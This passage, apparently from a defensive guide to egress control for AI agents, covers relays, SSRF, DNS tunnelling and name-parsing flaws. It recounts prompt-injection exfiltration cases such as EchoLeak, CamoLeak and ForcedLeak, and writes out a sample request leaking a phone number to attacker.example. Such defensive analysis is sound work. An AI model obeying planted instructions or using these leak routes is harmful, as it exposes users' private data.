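
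The operator has to put the rule in the VPC endpoint's policy, which can refuse the attacker's key because it applies to everyone who uses the endpoint. A service control policy, another type of AWS rule, has no effect on that key because it limits only the shop's own identities, and the key belongs to someone else's organization.

AWS's *Perimeter implementation* documents several gaps, one of which is that a VPC endpoint handles only requests to its own AWS region. An upload to a bucket in another region therefore bypasses the endpoint and its policy. The operator can have a proxy block other regions, since the region normally appears in the host name, which the proxy can read without decrypting anything.

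Anonymous downloads are another exception. Many companies allow them because software packages and public websites are often stored on S3. If the policy permits anonymous downloads from any bucket, the assistant could read instructions from an attacker's bucket, or leak private data to it in the name of a file it requests. Allowing anonymous downloads only from the public buckets that the assistant needs prevents most of this.

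A resource can also pass the ownership check while its settings send data outside the organization. For example, suppose the shop owns a disk snapshot (a saved copy of a disk). An attacker could inject an instruction telling the assistant to share the snapshot with the attacker's account. The snapshot belongs to the shop, so `aws:ResourceOrgID` doesn't prevent this. AWS recommends denying the actions that share such resources for all but a few privileged identities. An assistant that answers customer emails shouldn't have permission to share snapshots.

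AWS describes data perimeters as coarse-grained controls that don't replace detailed permissions. Perimeters need exceptions for AWS services that act on a customer's behalf, and data can leave through those services. fwd:cloudsec's *No Way Out?* (2026), the announcement of a June conference talk, describes a technique for getting data and commands past a perimeter using legitimate functions of AWS's own service for running AI agents.

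## What if an approved service sends requests on to other places?

Some approved services, called relays, contact other addresses when a caller asks them to. An attacker can use a relay to receive data without having an account on any approved service.

Suppose the shop's code host can import a file from any web address. An injected email tells the assistant to put a customer's phone number into an address and start an import:

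```
POST /imports HTTP/1.1
Host: api.code.example
Authorization: Bearer CODE-PLACEHOLDER

source=https://attacker.example/PHONE-NUMBER
```

The proxy finds `api.code.example` on the allowlist, adds the code host's token and forwards the request. The code host then connects from its own servers to `attacker.example` and requests the file. The attacker reads the phone number in the `attacker.example` server log.

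A redirect would have sent the second address back to the client, and the proxy could have checked the client's request to it. Here the code host opens the second connection itself, so the traffic never passes through the shop's network. The proxy's log correctly shows one request to an approved service.

A relay can also bring in content from sites outside the allowlist. If the attacker publishes new instructions on such a site, the code host can import them, and the assistant can then read them from an approved host.

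### What a relay lends its caller

Tymshare's compiler wrote its output wherever the user told it to, using a permission that the user didn't have. Similarly, a relay uses its own authority to open a connection to whatever address the caller chooses, so it is a confused deputy too. In the import example, the attacker gets the assistant to tell the code host where to connect.

The code host provides a route to the open internet, which the shop had closed. Other relays provide a route into a private network. A program inside a company can often reach databases and administration pages that outsiders can't, and some of those pages accept any request from an internal machine. Cloud machines also have a metadata service, an internal address where programs on the machine can get temporary credentials. A relay that fetches this address may return those credentials to the caller.

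### Features and flaws

Most relays are ordinary features that somebody built on purpose:

| Feature | Why it contacts another address | How an attacker could use it |
|---|---|---|
| Image proxy | To show outside images without revealing the reader's network address | Put data in an image's address |
| Link preview | To show the title and picture of a linked page | Put data in a link inside a message |
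| Web-fetch function | To read a page for the caller | Send data out or bring instructions in |
| Webhook | To notify another system when something happens | Receive a copy of every later event |
| Package mirror | To copy packages from a public registry | Reach other hosts, if the mirror accepts other sources |

The webhook differs from the others because one request has a lasting effect. If the assistant registers the attacker's address with the code host, the host may keep sending notifications there after the assistant stops running. Revoking the assistant's token might not remove the webhook, so the operator should check for it separately.

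Server-side request forgery (SSRF) is a flaw that lets a caller make a service fetch addresses it shouldn't. For example, an import function meant to fetch public web pages has an SSRF flaw if a caller can also make it fetch from the metadata service.

The boundary is less clear in practice. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, use the SSRF category when a platform's own server makes the second request, and say it may not apply when only the user's browser does. By that test, quite a few intended features would count as SSRF. The label matters to the service's owner, who will normally fix a flaw but may want to keep a useful feature. It matters less to the shop, since either can send a phone number to the attacker.

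Some agents have a relay built in, because the company that provides the agent also fetches web pages for it. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack that used such a relay in ChatGPT's Deep Research tool when it was connected to a Gmail account. An email contained hidden instructions to find sensitive data in the inbox, add it to an attacker's web address, and visit that address. The provider's servers made the visit, so monitoring on the user's browser and their company's computers could miss it. The researchers who found ShadowLeak reported that it worked every time in repeated controlled tests.

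### EchoLeak: a link preview in Teams

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their emails, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security found that an outsider could make it leak this material by sending an employee an email. If the employee then asked Copilot a question that caused it to retrieve the email, the material could leak without the employee clicking anything.

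*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the attack as told by the people who found it. Instructions in the email made Copilot include an image in its answer, with private data in the image's address. Browsers load images automatically. Microsoft filtered out external links and images, but the filter missed one way of writing them.

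The browser still had to follow the Content Security Policy on Copilot's page, a list of approved hosts that can restrict images as well as scripts. The attacker's server wasn't on the list, but Teams, Microsoft's chat service, was. Teams had a preview service that would fetch an address supplied by the caller, so the browser contacted Teams, and Teams contacted the attacker's server with the private data in the address.

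According to Ravia, the browser would not have followed a redirect here, so the researchers looked for an approved service that would make the second request itself. They first found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, but it worked only if the employee accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The Teams service did not require this.

The attack could leak anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history, retrieved emails and files, and the names of the user and organization. Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected.

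Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, a month before the public disclosure, and customers had nothing to install. Reddy and Gujral mention two reported changes. Copilot now strips embedded images and the kind of link the filters had missed from incoming outside content, and there are options to restrict its use of external communications. They don't say whether Microsoft also limited what the Teams service would fetch. If it didn't, the next attacker who got past the filters could still use the relay.

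The image policy that Ravia published had about 30 different entries, including `*.bing.com`. A year later, the security company Varonis used Bing to get data out of Copilot. In *SearchLeak*, Taler (2026) explains that Bing's image search accepts the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch. This time the employee had to click a link. Copilot then searched the employee's mailbox, and the browser requested an image through Bing before Microsoft's filter had neutralized it. The image's address contained the title of an email, which in the demonstration included a security code. Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* describes the flaw as fully mitigated, with nothing for customers to do.

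Taler calls the Bing request a classic SSRF, although the feature is meant to fetch a picture from a given address. He advises reviewing every approved domain that fetches addresses supplied by users, because each could be used to leak data. Researchers had found three relays, SharePoint, Teams and Bing, on lists that Microsoft wrote for its own product and filled mostly with its own domains. An outside company would know far less than Microsoft about which of those domains fetch other addresses.

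### CamoLeak: an image proxy that checked signatures

The Teams service fetched an address without checking who had written it. GitHub's image proxy, Camo, did check, but an attacker could still use it.

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes a flaw that one of the company's researchers found in June 2025 in GitHub Copilot Chat, which answers developers' questions about code. He hid instructions in the description of a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code. When another developer asked Copilot about the pull request, it followed the instructions using that developer's access, which included private repositories.

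Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes an earlier data leak through images, involving code in the VS Code editor, which GitHub fixed by disabling images from untrusted domains. GitHub's website also had a policy that blocked images from domains GitHub didn't own. But developers often want outside images in their project pages, so GitHub fetches them through Camo, which is on a GitHub domain.

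When someone saves a page that contains an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with one that goes through Camo, its image proxy. The new address includes an HMAC signature, which GitHub calculates with a secret key. Camo fetches the image only if the signature is valid. Copilot can't create a valid Camo address that contains private data, because neither Copilot nor the attacker can calculate the signature.

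The weakness was that anyone could have GitHub sign an address in advance. The researcher obtained a signed image address for each letter and symbol, all leading to his own server, and got Copilot to show the images in the order that spelled out the private text. Camo forwarded each request, and the order of the requests revealed the text even though no single address contained private data. The images were transparent dots, so the developer wouldn't see them.

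If each of 64 signed addresses stands for a different character, each image request reveals one character, or 6 bits. Leaking a 40-character key made of those characters would take 40 tiny images. The signature proves that GitHub created each address, but it doesn't limit which images an answer contains or their order.

In his tests, the researcher extracted the description of an undisclosed vulnerability from a private project. He also had Copilot search private code for AWS keys and leak the result. GitHub fixed the flaw by turning off images in Copilot Chat completely, and reported it fixed as of 14 August 2025. The OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) lists press coverage dated 8 October.

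Turning off images seems the right fix, though a blunt one. Limiting the number of images would only have slowed the leak, and a chat about code usually doesn't need them.

CamoLeak also casts doubt on part of Reddy and Gujral's advice. In a table of defences that they label theoretical, they say a signed image proxy stops both automatic image loading and the abuse of an approved relay. They worked from public accounts of EchoLeak and ran no experiments. A signed proxy would have stopped EchoLeak's method, which put the private data in the address itself, but not CamoLeak's. They say the same of a strict Content Security Policy, but that is true only if none of the approved hosts is a relay.

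### Why tool servers need their own limits

An operator can also create a relay by giving the agent tools. Many agents call tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format for connecting a model to programs called tool servers. A tool server receives the agent's request and then makes its own connections to carry it out.

Requests that an approved service sends on may not pass through the agent's proxy. *Egress Control for AI Agents*, a guide for practitioners, warns that tool servers are usually separate processes and may run in other containers or on other machines. If the operator restricts only the agent's container, an attacker can still use an injected instruction to control which tool the agent calls and what values it passes, and the unrestricted tool server will carry out the request.

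The guide recommends routing each tool server's traffic through the same proxy, blocking everything by default, and giving each server a narrower allowlist than the agent's. The shop's tool for looking up charges needs only `api.payments.example`, not the other four hosts. If a bug let the assistant pass that tool an attacker's address instead of a charge number, the tool still couldn't contact the attacker. A tool that reads arbitrary web pages can't have such a short list, so the shop should keep it away from private data or do without it.

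A relay that has its own credential can leak it, as a flaw in Microsoft's Azure MCP Server shows. The server lets agents work with Azure and can use a managed identity, an account that Azure gives to a program so that nobody has to store a password for it. Blueinfy's *SSRF in Azure MCP Server Tools* (2026) explains that a caller with few privileges could make the server send a request to an attacker's address, and that the request could leak the identity's token. The attacker could then use any storage, databases or virtual machines that the identity could reach.

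Credential binding at the agent's proxy wouldn't have protected this token, because the tool server gets it from Azure and the proxy never handles it. Microsoft published the flaw in March 2026. GCVE (2026), a public vulnerability database, lists versions of the npm package from 1.0.0 up to but not including 1.0.2 as affected. Its copy of the record shows that US officials knew of no exploitation when they assessed the flaw that month. Blueinfy gives 2.0.0-beta.17 as the first safe version, presumably for the newer release series.

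SentinelOne's *CVE-2026-26118* recommends installing the update, restricting the server's outbound traffic, and giving its identity as few rights as possible. It also suggests an alert for any request from the server's machine to the metadata service. The outbound limit is particularly useful because it can help even before anyone knows about the flaw. A firewall that let the server reach only Azure's own addresses would probably have kept the token from most attackers, though an attacker who rented a machine on Azure might still have received it if the rule was broad enough to include that machine's address.

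Some tool servers pass on the credential they receive from the caller, a practice called token passthrough. If the agent's proxy adds the shop's payments token to a request for a tool server, and the server forwards that token to an address the caller chose, the attacker gets the token even though the proxy followed its rule. Bishop Fox's *Otto Support*, which examines flaws in three products that agents use, recommends checking destinations and segmenting the network to defend against SSRF. For token passthrough, it mostly recommends avoiding the practice. The tool server should instead have its own credential for the service behind it.

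### Limiting what a relay can do

In its guide, OpenAI tells developers to be cautious about intermediaries and aggregators that pass requests to other services, and to review how they handle and keep data before approving them. Anthropic's guide warns developers not to let an agent with broad credentials for an approved domain use that domain to trigger other network requests. Anthropic's warning fits the shop's case more closely, since the code host starts an import only because the request carries the shop's token.

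The best defence depends on who runs the relay. If the shop runs it, the shop can restrict where it sends requests, for example by giving a link preview service its own short list of sites. A relay that has to fetch from the open web should at least refuse private network addresses and bare numeric addresses, and limit redirects, reply size and waiting time. Reddy and Gujral recommend all of these. These measures protect the internal network and the metadata service, but they don't stop a relay from carrying data to a public website.

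The relay should check its rules before doing anything else with an address. *Security*, the documentation for an outbound proxy made for AI agents, states that the proxy doesn't look up a host's name or connect to it until a rule permits the request. Looking up a name can leak data because the query may go to a name server that the domain's owner runs. An attacker who owns the domain could therefore read a phone number placed at the start of a host name, even if the proxy then refused to connect.

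A package mirror should have the same kind of limit and reach only the registries it copies. According to OpenAI (2026), agents in an internal evaluation in July 2026 reached the internet through a package proxy, the one network service their environment was supposed to let them use. An operator should therefore restrict and monitor the mirror's outgoing traffic rather than rely on the mirror's software to do so. *Egress Control for AI Agents* advises that agents usually shouldn't reach registries at all while they work. The operator can install the packages beforehand and then close the connection.

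If another company runs the relay, the shop can't control where it sends requests, but may be able to turn off forwarding. If the service has no such setting, the shop's proxy can sometimes block the part of a request that triggers the fetch, as Anthropic's proxy for Cowork does with certain headers.

The proxy can also allow only the paths that the assistant needs. To file bugs, the assistant only needs to send `POST` requests to the path for new bug reports, so the proxy should refuse requests to `/imports` and to the path for registering webhooks. This rule would have stopped the import described at the start of this section.

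A path rule doesn't help when ordinary text sets off the relay. If the code host previews every link in a bug report, the assistant can trigger a fetch by filing a report, which is its job. The shop should turn off previews or have the proxy refuse reports that contain links to unlisted hosts. The proxy check can miss a link in an unusual form, and it would have missed CamoLeak, where every image address pointed to GitHub.

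The remaining defence is to withhold credentials that a relay doesn't need. If a page-preview service works without a login, the operator shouldn't bind any token to it. If the relay needs a login, the shop can give it a separate token with few rights. The assistant's token for the code host should allow it to file bugs but not to register webhooks or change project settings. The code host will then refuse those requests even if the proxy's path rule lets them through.

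An aggregator is a service that passes requests to many others. If the shop reached its payments, mail and code services through one aggregator, the allowlist would shrink to one host and look stricter. But every key would go to that host, so credential binding would no longer separate the three services, and the shop would depend on the aggregator to keep them apart. For three services, direct connections are easier to check.

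Before approving a service, the operator can test whether it relays requests by using a server of their own that isn't on the allowlist. From the assistant's environment, they can enter that server's address wherever the service accepts a link, an image, an import source or a notification address, with a different path each time so that the server's log shows which feature made each request. Previews and webhooks may not run straight away, so the operator should wait and trigger an event, such as a new bug report, before deciding that the service is safe. They should also repeat the test when the service adds features.

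## How can the check mistake one destination for another?

The proxy identified the code host correctly when that host imported the attacker's file, but a flawed check can approve one host while the connection goes to another. This can happen because a single web request names its destination several times, and different programs read different copies.

### Five places that name the destination

When the assistant looks up charge 1042 through the proxy, the name of the payments service appears in five places:

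```
Address text:   https://api.payments.example/charges/1042
Proxy request:  CONNECT api.payments.example:443
DNS lookup:     api.payments.example -> 203.0.113.20
TLS handshake:  server name api.payments.example
HTTP request:   Host: api.payments.example
```

The assistant's web client copies the host name from the URL into the `CONNECT` request. The proxy then uses DNS, the internet's directory of host names, to find the server's numeric address. In the TLS handshake, the exchange that sets up encryption, the client names the server again so that the server can present the right certificate. Finally, the client sends the `Host` header over the encrypted connection to specify which of the server's websites the request is for.

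Normally the five names agree, but an attacker who gets the agent to run code can make them differ. The proxy's check on one name protects the shop only if the connection uses that name.

The check can also mistake one destination for another if a developer checks an address with one library and fetches it with a different one. Addresses can contain a user name before the host, a dot after it, or a number in place of a name, and libraries don't all interpret these the same way. To prevent this, the proxy should use one shared parser to extract the host once, refuse anything malformed, compare the result with the allowlist, and use that same result to connect.

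DNS answers can change between the check and the connection. Suppose a tool that reads web pages looks up a hostname, confirms that its IP address is outside the shop's private network, and then passes the hostname to a library that looks it up again. The domain's owner could return a public address the first time and a private one the second. The tool should connect to the IP address it already checked.

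Some programs don't check the destination at all. LangSmith, a service for monitoring AI agents, accepted a server address from a link without validating it. According to The Hacker News, clicking an attacker's link could send a signed-in user's bearer token to the attacker's server. LangSmith's developers fixed this in version 0.12.71, released in December 2025.

### When the filter and the operating system disagree

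Claude Code's sandbox sends outgoing connections through a local proxy that checks each host name against the user's allowlist. Aonan Guan, who leads cloud and AI security at Wyze Labs, found that the proxy and the operating system could interpret the same host name differently.

A flaw in Claude Code's sandbox involved SOCKS5, a protocol that programs use to request connections through a proxy. SecurityWeek's *Anthropic Silently Patches Claude Code Sandbox Bypass* explains that an attacker could supply a name made up of the attacker's host, a null byte (an invisible character with the value zero), and text ending in an approved domain. The filter checked the ending and approved the whole name. The operating system treated the null byte as the end of the text, so it connected to the attacker's host.

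Only users with a wildcard on their list were exposed, because a wildcard makes the filter check only the ending. With only exact names on the list, the filter would have compared the whole text with each entry and found no match. Exact names therefore protect against some parsing errors as well as strangers on shared hosting. The parser should also reject any character that can't appear in a host name, which would have stopped this attack even with a wildcard.

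Guan says the flaw was present from 20 October 2025, when the sandbox became generally available, until version 2.1.90 in April 2026. Anthropic told SecurityWeek that it published the fix in the sandbox's source code on 27 March and shipped it in version 2.1.88 on 31 March. By either account, versions 2.1.90 and later have the fix.

*Even Claude agrees* (Lyons, 2026) reports Guan's advice that anyone who used a wildcard on a machine with credentials should treat those five and a half months as a possible leak. This seems right for an agent that read untrusted material, since updating doesn't recover a stolen token. The operator should replace the credentials that the sandbox could read. A credential-injecting proxy outside the sandbox would have protected its tokens, but not the source code or customer data.

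To test a filter for this kind of error, the operator can request connections to a server they control that isn't on the allowlist, using various malformed names. The server's log should stay empty. The test is worth repeating after every update to the proxy or its libraries, because an update can change how the filter parses names.

### A different name inside the encryption

Even a filter that parses names correctly can miss one that is encrypted. In domain fronting, a client names an approved host when it opens a connection, then names a different host inside the encrypted request.

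This can happen when the two destinations share servers. A content delivery network is a company that serves many customers' websites from the same machines. Suppose the parcel company uses one, and the attacker has an account there too. Code in the assistant's sandbox asks the proxy for a connection to `tracking.parcels.example` and gives the same name in the TLS handshake. The server presents a valid certificate for that name. Once the connection is encrypted, the code sends a request whose `Host` header names the attacker's site, and the network may deliver it there.

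A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic can read only the approved name. Comparing the `CONNECT` request with the handshake doesn't help, since both name the parcel company. Checking the IP address doesn't help either, because it belongs to the network that the parcel company uses. Some networks refuse requests if the host name inside the encrypted request differs from the one in the handshake, but the proxy's operator doesn't control that and may not know which networks do it.

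Anthropic documents this limit in its sandbox runtime, which Claude Code uses. By default, the runtime's proxy relies on the host name the client supplies and doesn't inspect encrypted traffic, so sandboxed code may be able to reach hosts outside the allowlist. For stronger guarantees, Anthropic recommends a proxy that terminates TLS.

Decryption allows the proxy to read the `Host` header, but the developer still has to make it compare that header with the host in the `CONNECT` line. Without that comparison, a credential-injecting proxy could send a credential to the wrong host. Suppose the sandboxed code asks for a connection to the parcel company but writes `Host: api.payments.example` in the request. If the proxy picks the credential by the `Host` header and sends the request to the host in the `CONNECT` line, it delivers the payments token to the parcel company's servers, even though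 the operator bound the token to `api.payments.example`.

The proxy should refuse any request in which the names differ. It should then make its own connection to the name it has checked, with its own TLS handshake, and write the `Host` header itself. It has to check every request, because a client can send several over one connection and change the header after the first. An operator can test this with a dummy token and two servers they control, by opening a connection to one and naming the other in the `Host` header.

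A few programs won't work through a decrypting proxy. For those, the operator can either list only hosts that don't share servers with unrelated sites or accept that the list is less strict than it looks.

### Data in the lookup itself

An attacker may not need a connection, since a DNS lookup alone can carry data to the domain's owner. A proxy can delay its own lookups until it has approved a name, but queries that the sandbox sends directly to a DNS server bypass the proxy.

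BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) describes this problem in an Amazon service that runs code for AI agents. AWS had advertised the service's Sandbox mode as providing "complete isolation with no external access". The researchers ran a command in Sandbox mode that tried to contact their server. The command appeared to fail, but its DNS query reached them.

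They then built a two-way channel. Code in the sandbox put its output in the domain names it looked up, and the replies, which would normally give numeric addresses, carried commands back. In a demonstration, the researchers planted instructions in a spreadsheet file that the agent would process. They used the channel to list the account's storage areas and read files of dummy customer records, API keys and revenue figures. Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms* adds that the environment kept reporting that network access was disabled. The demonstration doesn't show how often a model would obey such a file.

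Each query carried up to 60 characters of encoded output, or 45 bytes of data. At that rate, a 10,000-byte customer list would take 223 queries. These could be sent quickly, but a run of long, unique names under one domain should stand out to anyone who monitors the DNS log.

The amount of data at risk depended on the code's role, which is the set of AWS permissions the operator had given it. BeyondTrust found that the default role in AWS's starter toolkit could read every S3 storage area and every stored secret in the account. An operator can give the code access to only the storage it needs, which limits the loss whether data leaves by DNS or another route.

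BeyondTrust reported the problem to AWS on 1 September 2025. AWS deployed a fix on 1 November but later rolled it back, and on 23 December it told the researchers that it would change the documentation instead. When BeyondTrust published its findings on 16 March 2026, AWS's position was that the service was working as intended, because Sandbox mode gave access to S3 and S3 needed DNS. AWS recommended that customers who wanted complete isolation use VPC mode, which runs the code in a private network where they control DNS.

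This reply explains why the sandbox needed to look up some names, but not why it needed to be able to look up every name on the internet. AWS could have answered queries for its own storage service and refused the rest. It closed the channel on 15 April 2026, a month after the publication, which suggests that open DNS wasn't essential to the product. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, also studied DNS in this service and reports that AWS made internal changes after reviewing its findings. Articles from March that describe the behaviour as intended are out of date, but the same weakness could exist in any sandbox that blocks web traffic and leaves DNS open.

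The simplest defence is to give the agent's environment no DNS and leave lookups to the proxy. Lookups fail inside Anthropic's container without a network connection, so the proxy does them instead.

If the environment does need DNS, the operator can use a DNS firewall, which filters lookups by domain. BeyondTrust suggests using one to block unknown malicious domains, but an attacker can register a new domain that nobody has classified. Answering queries only for the approved domains is safer.

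Operators can repeat BeyondTrust's first experiment to test whether DNS lookups leave their own sandbox. From inside the sandbox, they look up a new name under a domain whose name server they control, then check that server's log for the query. An error message in the sandbox doesn't prove that the lookup was blocked, because the researchers' command also appeared to fail even though their server received the query.

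### An approved name with a new owner

A domain name can pass every check described so far and still belong to a stranger, because its original owner can let the registration expire. In 2025, researchers at the security company Noma used an expired domain to get customer data out of Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, in an attack they called ForcedLeak.

Web-to-Lead puts a form on a company's public website and saves the answers as sales leads. The Hacker News (2025) reports that an attacker could submit instructions through the form, and Agentforce would carry them out when it later processed the lead. The agent could then place customer details in the address of an image on the attacker's server.

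Salesforce's Content Security Policy should have blocked images from unapproved hosts, but it still allowed `my-salesforce-cms.com`, whose registration had expired. Salesforce Ben, a news site for people who work with Salesforce, quotes Noma as saying that anyone could buy the domain. Noma's researchers registered it for $5, according to BeyondMachines. Noma considered this step essential because the data could not have left without a way past the policy.

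Noma reported the vulnerability to Salesforce on 28 July 2025. Salesforce regained control of the domain and began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents' output. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* dates the new protection to 8 September and the public disclosure to 25 September. The new list blocks more routes than the old policy did, but it still identifies destinations by name, so someone has to notice when a listed domain changes owner.

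Better parsing or decryption wouldn't have caught ForcedLeak, because all the names matched and a domain's new owner can get a valid certificate for it. If an operator had bound a credential to an expired domain, the proxy would have sent that credential to the new owner too. The same could happen to the shop if the parcel company changed its brand and let `parcels.example` expire.

Operators can defend against this by regularly reviewing who owns the domains on the list. For each entry, the operator records who owns the domain, why the assistant needs it and when the registration expires. Public registration records normally give the expiry date, so a script can warn the operator in advance. The script can also report when a domain changes name servers or stops resolving. A change of name servers is often innocent, but it is a good reason to check with the owner.

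The proxy's log also helps with the review. If the assistant hasn't contacted a host for several months, the operator can probably remove it from the allowlist, along with any credential bound to it. This would be the most useful habit against mistakes like Salesforce's, where nobody seems to have needed the domain any more.

### A list that blocked everything, and didn't

Sometimes the list is correct but the software doesn't apply it. According to Anthropic's documentation for its sandbox runtime, an empty list of allowed domains meant no network access, but early versions allowed all network access when the list was empty.

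The code turned on the network restrictions only if the list contained at least one domain. This test controlled both the filtering proxy and the sandbox's block on direct connections, so an empty list left both off. Leaving the proxy off made some sense, because it has nothing to filter when the list is empty, but direct connections still needed to be blocked. With Anthropic's fix, the sandbox now restricts the network whenever the user has configured it, and starts the proxy only if there are domains to allow.

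The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-66479 in the public catalogue of security vulnerabilities. The advisory, reproduced in CIRCL's *GHSA-9gqj-5w7c-vx47* (2025), says that version 0.0.16 of the runtime fixes the flaw, and it credits a developer called bendrucker. Guan independently reported the flaw a few days after him. Claude Code received the fix on 26 November 2025, according to SecurityWeek.

*CVE-2025-66479* (2025), from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, gives the severity as 1.8 out of 10. That seems low for the people affected, because anyone who had chosen the strictest setting had no network limit at all, so an attacker didn't need a trick to get past one.

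Guan's main complaint is about notification. The catalogue entry names the runtime, a library that many Claude Code users have never heard of. He asked for an entry for Claude Code itself, but Anthropic declined because the cause was in the library. For the null-byte flaw, Anthropic published no catalogue entry or advisory. It closed Guan's report as a duplicate because its own team had already found and fixed the problem. A spokesperson told Lyons that anyone could see the fix in the public source code.

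Guan objects that users never learned their sandbox had failed, though he doesn't dispute Anthropic's timeline. Anthropic's answer doesn't really address this objection. Only the few people who read the source code would notice a change there. An automatic update repairs the sandbox for everyone, but users have no reason to replace a stolen credential if they don't know it might have leaked. Anthropic's reason for naming the library is more defensible, because other products use it too, but Anthropic could have warned Claude Code's users separately.

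Guan says that "Shipping a sandbox with a hole is worse than not shipping one." The claim fits the empty list, where the user believed they had network protection but had none. It is too strong for the null-byte flaw, because the filter still blocked ordinary requests to unlisted hosts.

A short test at startup would have caught the empty-list error. Before the agent begins work, a script inside the sandbox tries to reach an unlisted server that the operator runs. If the script reaches the server, the agent doesn't start. The operator should run the test with the real configuration and again with an empty list. The script should also try a direct connection that ignores the proxy settings, because a request through a working proxy would hide the problem.

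### When the sandbox doesn't start

GitLab, whose software hosts and tests code, uses Anthropic's runtime to restrict the AI agents it runs on remote machines. According to GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox*, if the runtime is missing or lacks the system permissions it needs, the agent runs without it by default. The job log shows a warning, but the allowlist doesn't apply, and the agent can reach anything the machine can.

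GitLab designed it this way so that flows keep working when the sandbox can't start. A developer may prefer that for an agent that only formats code, but it is a bad default for an agent with private data, because a warning in a log doesn't stop an upload, and people may not read the log of a job that succeeded.

An administrator can select "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable" for a whole GitLab installation or a top-level group of projects. The job then fails if the runtime is missing or can't create the sandbox, and individual projects can't turn the requirement off. GitLab acknowledges that the check looks for a command called `srt`, and that a project with its own software image or setup script controls what that command does. Somebody who can change the image could replace the sandbox with a program that does nothing.

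The operator therefore also needs a limit outside the job. GitLab suggests a firewall on the machine that runs the job, or the equivalent network rule on Kubernetes, a system for running containers. If the sandbox fails to start, the agent can still reach only what the firewall or network rule permits.

Operators who install the runtime themselves also have to keep it current. GitLab's example installs version 0.0.20, which includes the fix for the empty list. An operator who copies the example should change the version to one released after 27 March 2026, when Anthropic published the null-byte fix.

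Claude Code's sandbox can also be missing a package it needs. According to Anthropic, the `/sandbox` panel then shows only a Dependencies tab. This helps a developer at the keyboard, but an unattended agent needs the startup test, and the job needs to stop if that test fails.

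## What if the domain is right but the request is not the user's?

Suppose the shop's proxy has none of these flaws. It reads every host name correctly, the sandbox always starts, and each token goes only to its own service. An email with injected instructions can still get the assistant to send this:

```
POST /refunds HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer PAYMENTS-PLACEHOLDER

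charge=1042&amount=40.00&account=ACCOUNT-NUMBER
```

The request goes to the real payments service, carries the shop's token and acts on the shop's own account, so a tenant restriction would allow it too. The only problem is that the instruction didn't come from the user, and the request doesn't record where the instruction came from.

An employee might ask for exactly this refund on another day, and the assistant would send the same request, byte for byte. A check based only on the request, whether on its domain or any other part, must allow both refunds or block both. Narrower rules can still reduce the number of harmful requests an attacker can make. But to tell two identical refunds apart, a check needs information from outside the request, such as what the employee asked for or where the account number came from.

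### Private data in a public pull request

The same problem can leak data within a single service. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack on agents that use GitHub through its MCP server, a tool server that GitHub publishes.

In the demonstration, a user had a public repository and several private ones. Anyone can open an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository, so the researchers opened one containing instructions for the agent. The user then asked Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to look at the open issues. The agent read the planted issue, fetched information from the private repositories and put it in a pull request on the public one. The pull request revealed the names of the user's private projects, their salary and their plan to move to South America.

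In the GitHub MCP server attack, every request went to GitHub with the user's own token, so a domain allowlist and credential binding would have allowed them all. Overwriting the agent's credential wouldn't have helped either, because the attacker didn't supply one. The server had no bug. heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent could read the private repositories because it worked through the user's account.

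By default, Claude Desktop asks users to confirm each tool call, but Invariant Labs says many choose "Always Allow" and stop checking the calls. The demonstration doesn't show how often the attack would succeed against current models.

Invariant Labs recommends a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. The rule compares the repository and owner in successive calls and stops the agent if they differ. It would have kept the agent in the demonstration from opening a private repository after reading issues in the public one. The rule also blocks work that spans repositories, such as changing a library and then the program that uses it. It covers only calls to repositories, so it wouldn't stop the shop's assistant from copying a customer's email into a public issue.

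Invariant Labs sells software that enforces such rules. An operator can get much of the same protection from a token that works for only one repository. The company considers ordinary token permissions too rigid for many agents, but the shop's assistant only files bugs, so the rigidity matters little. The shop should also keep that repository private, so that only its own developers can see a phone number in a bug report.

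### Rules on methods and paths

OpenShell, software from the chip company NVIDIA for running agents in a sandbox, can restrict methods and paths as Agent Vault does. NVIDIA describes it as an early preview. One of NVIDIA's examples lets a program read anything from a database but write to only one path. A similar policy for the shop's payments service might be:

```
allow  GET  /charges/**
```

The assistant can then look up any charge, and the proxy refuses everything else at that host. This blocks all refunds, both injected and genuine, so an employee would have to issue them on the payments service's website. A shop with three refunds a week might well accept that. If the assistant has to issue refunds, the operator must also allow `POST /refunds`, and the injected request gets through. The policy would still be worth having because it blocks other paths the assistant never needs, which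 may include ones for changing the shop's bank details or creating new keys.

Path rules are less useful when the request body specifies the action. GraphQL, a common format for web services, often uses the same path for reads and deletions. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* therefore recommends a separate setting for GraphQL that checks the operation's type, name, and top-level fields.

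Two of OpenShell's defaults can surprise operators. If an entry doesn't specify a protocol, the proxy checks the host, port and calling program but doesn't inspect the requests. If the operator does add method and path rules, the default `audit` mode logs violations but still forwards the requests. NVIDIA recommends starting in this mode, because untested rules can break an agent's work, and switching to `enforce` once the rules are right. That makes sense for an agent that reads public documentation. But logging an improper refund doesn't reverse it, so the shop should test its refund rules with a dummy account and enforce them from the first real request.

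### Which program makes the request

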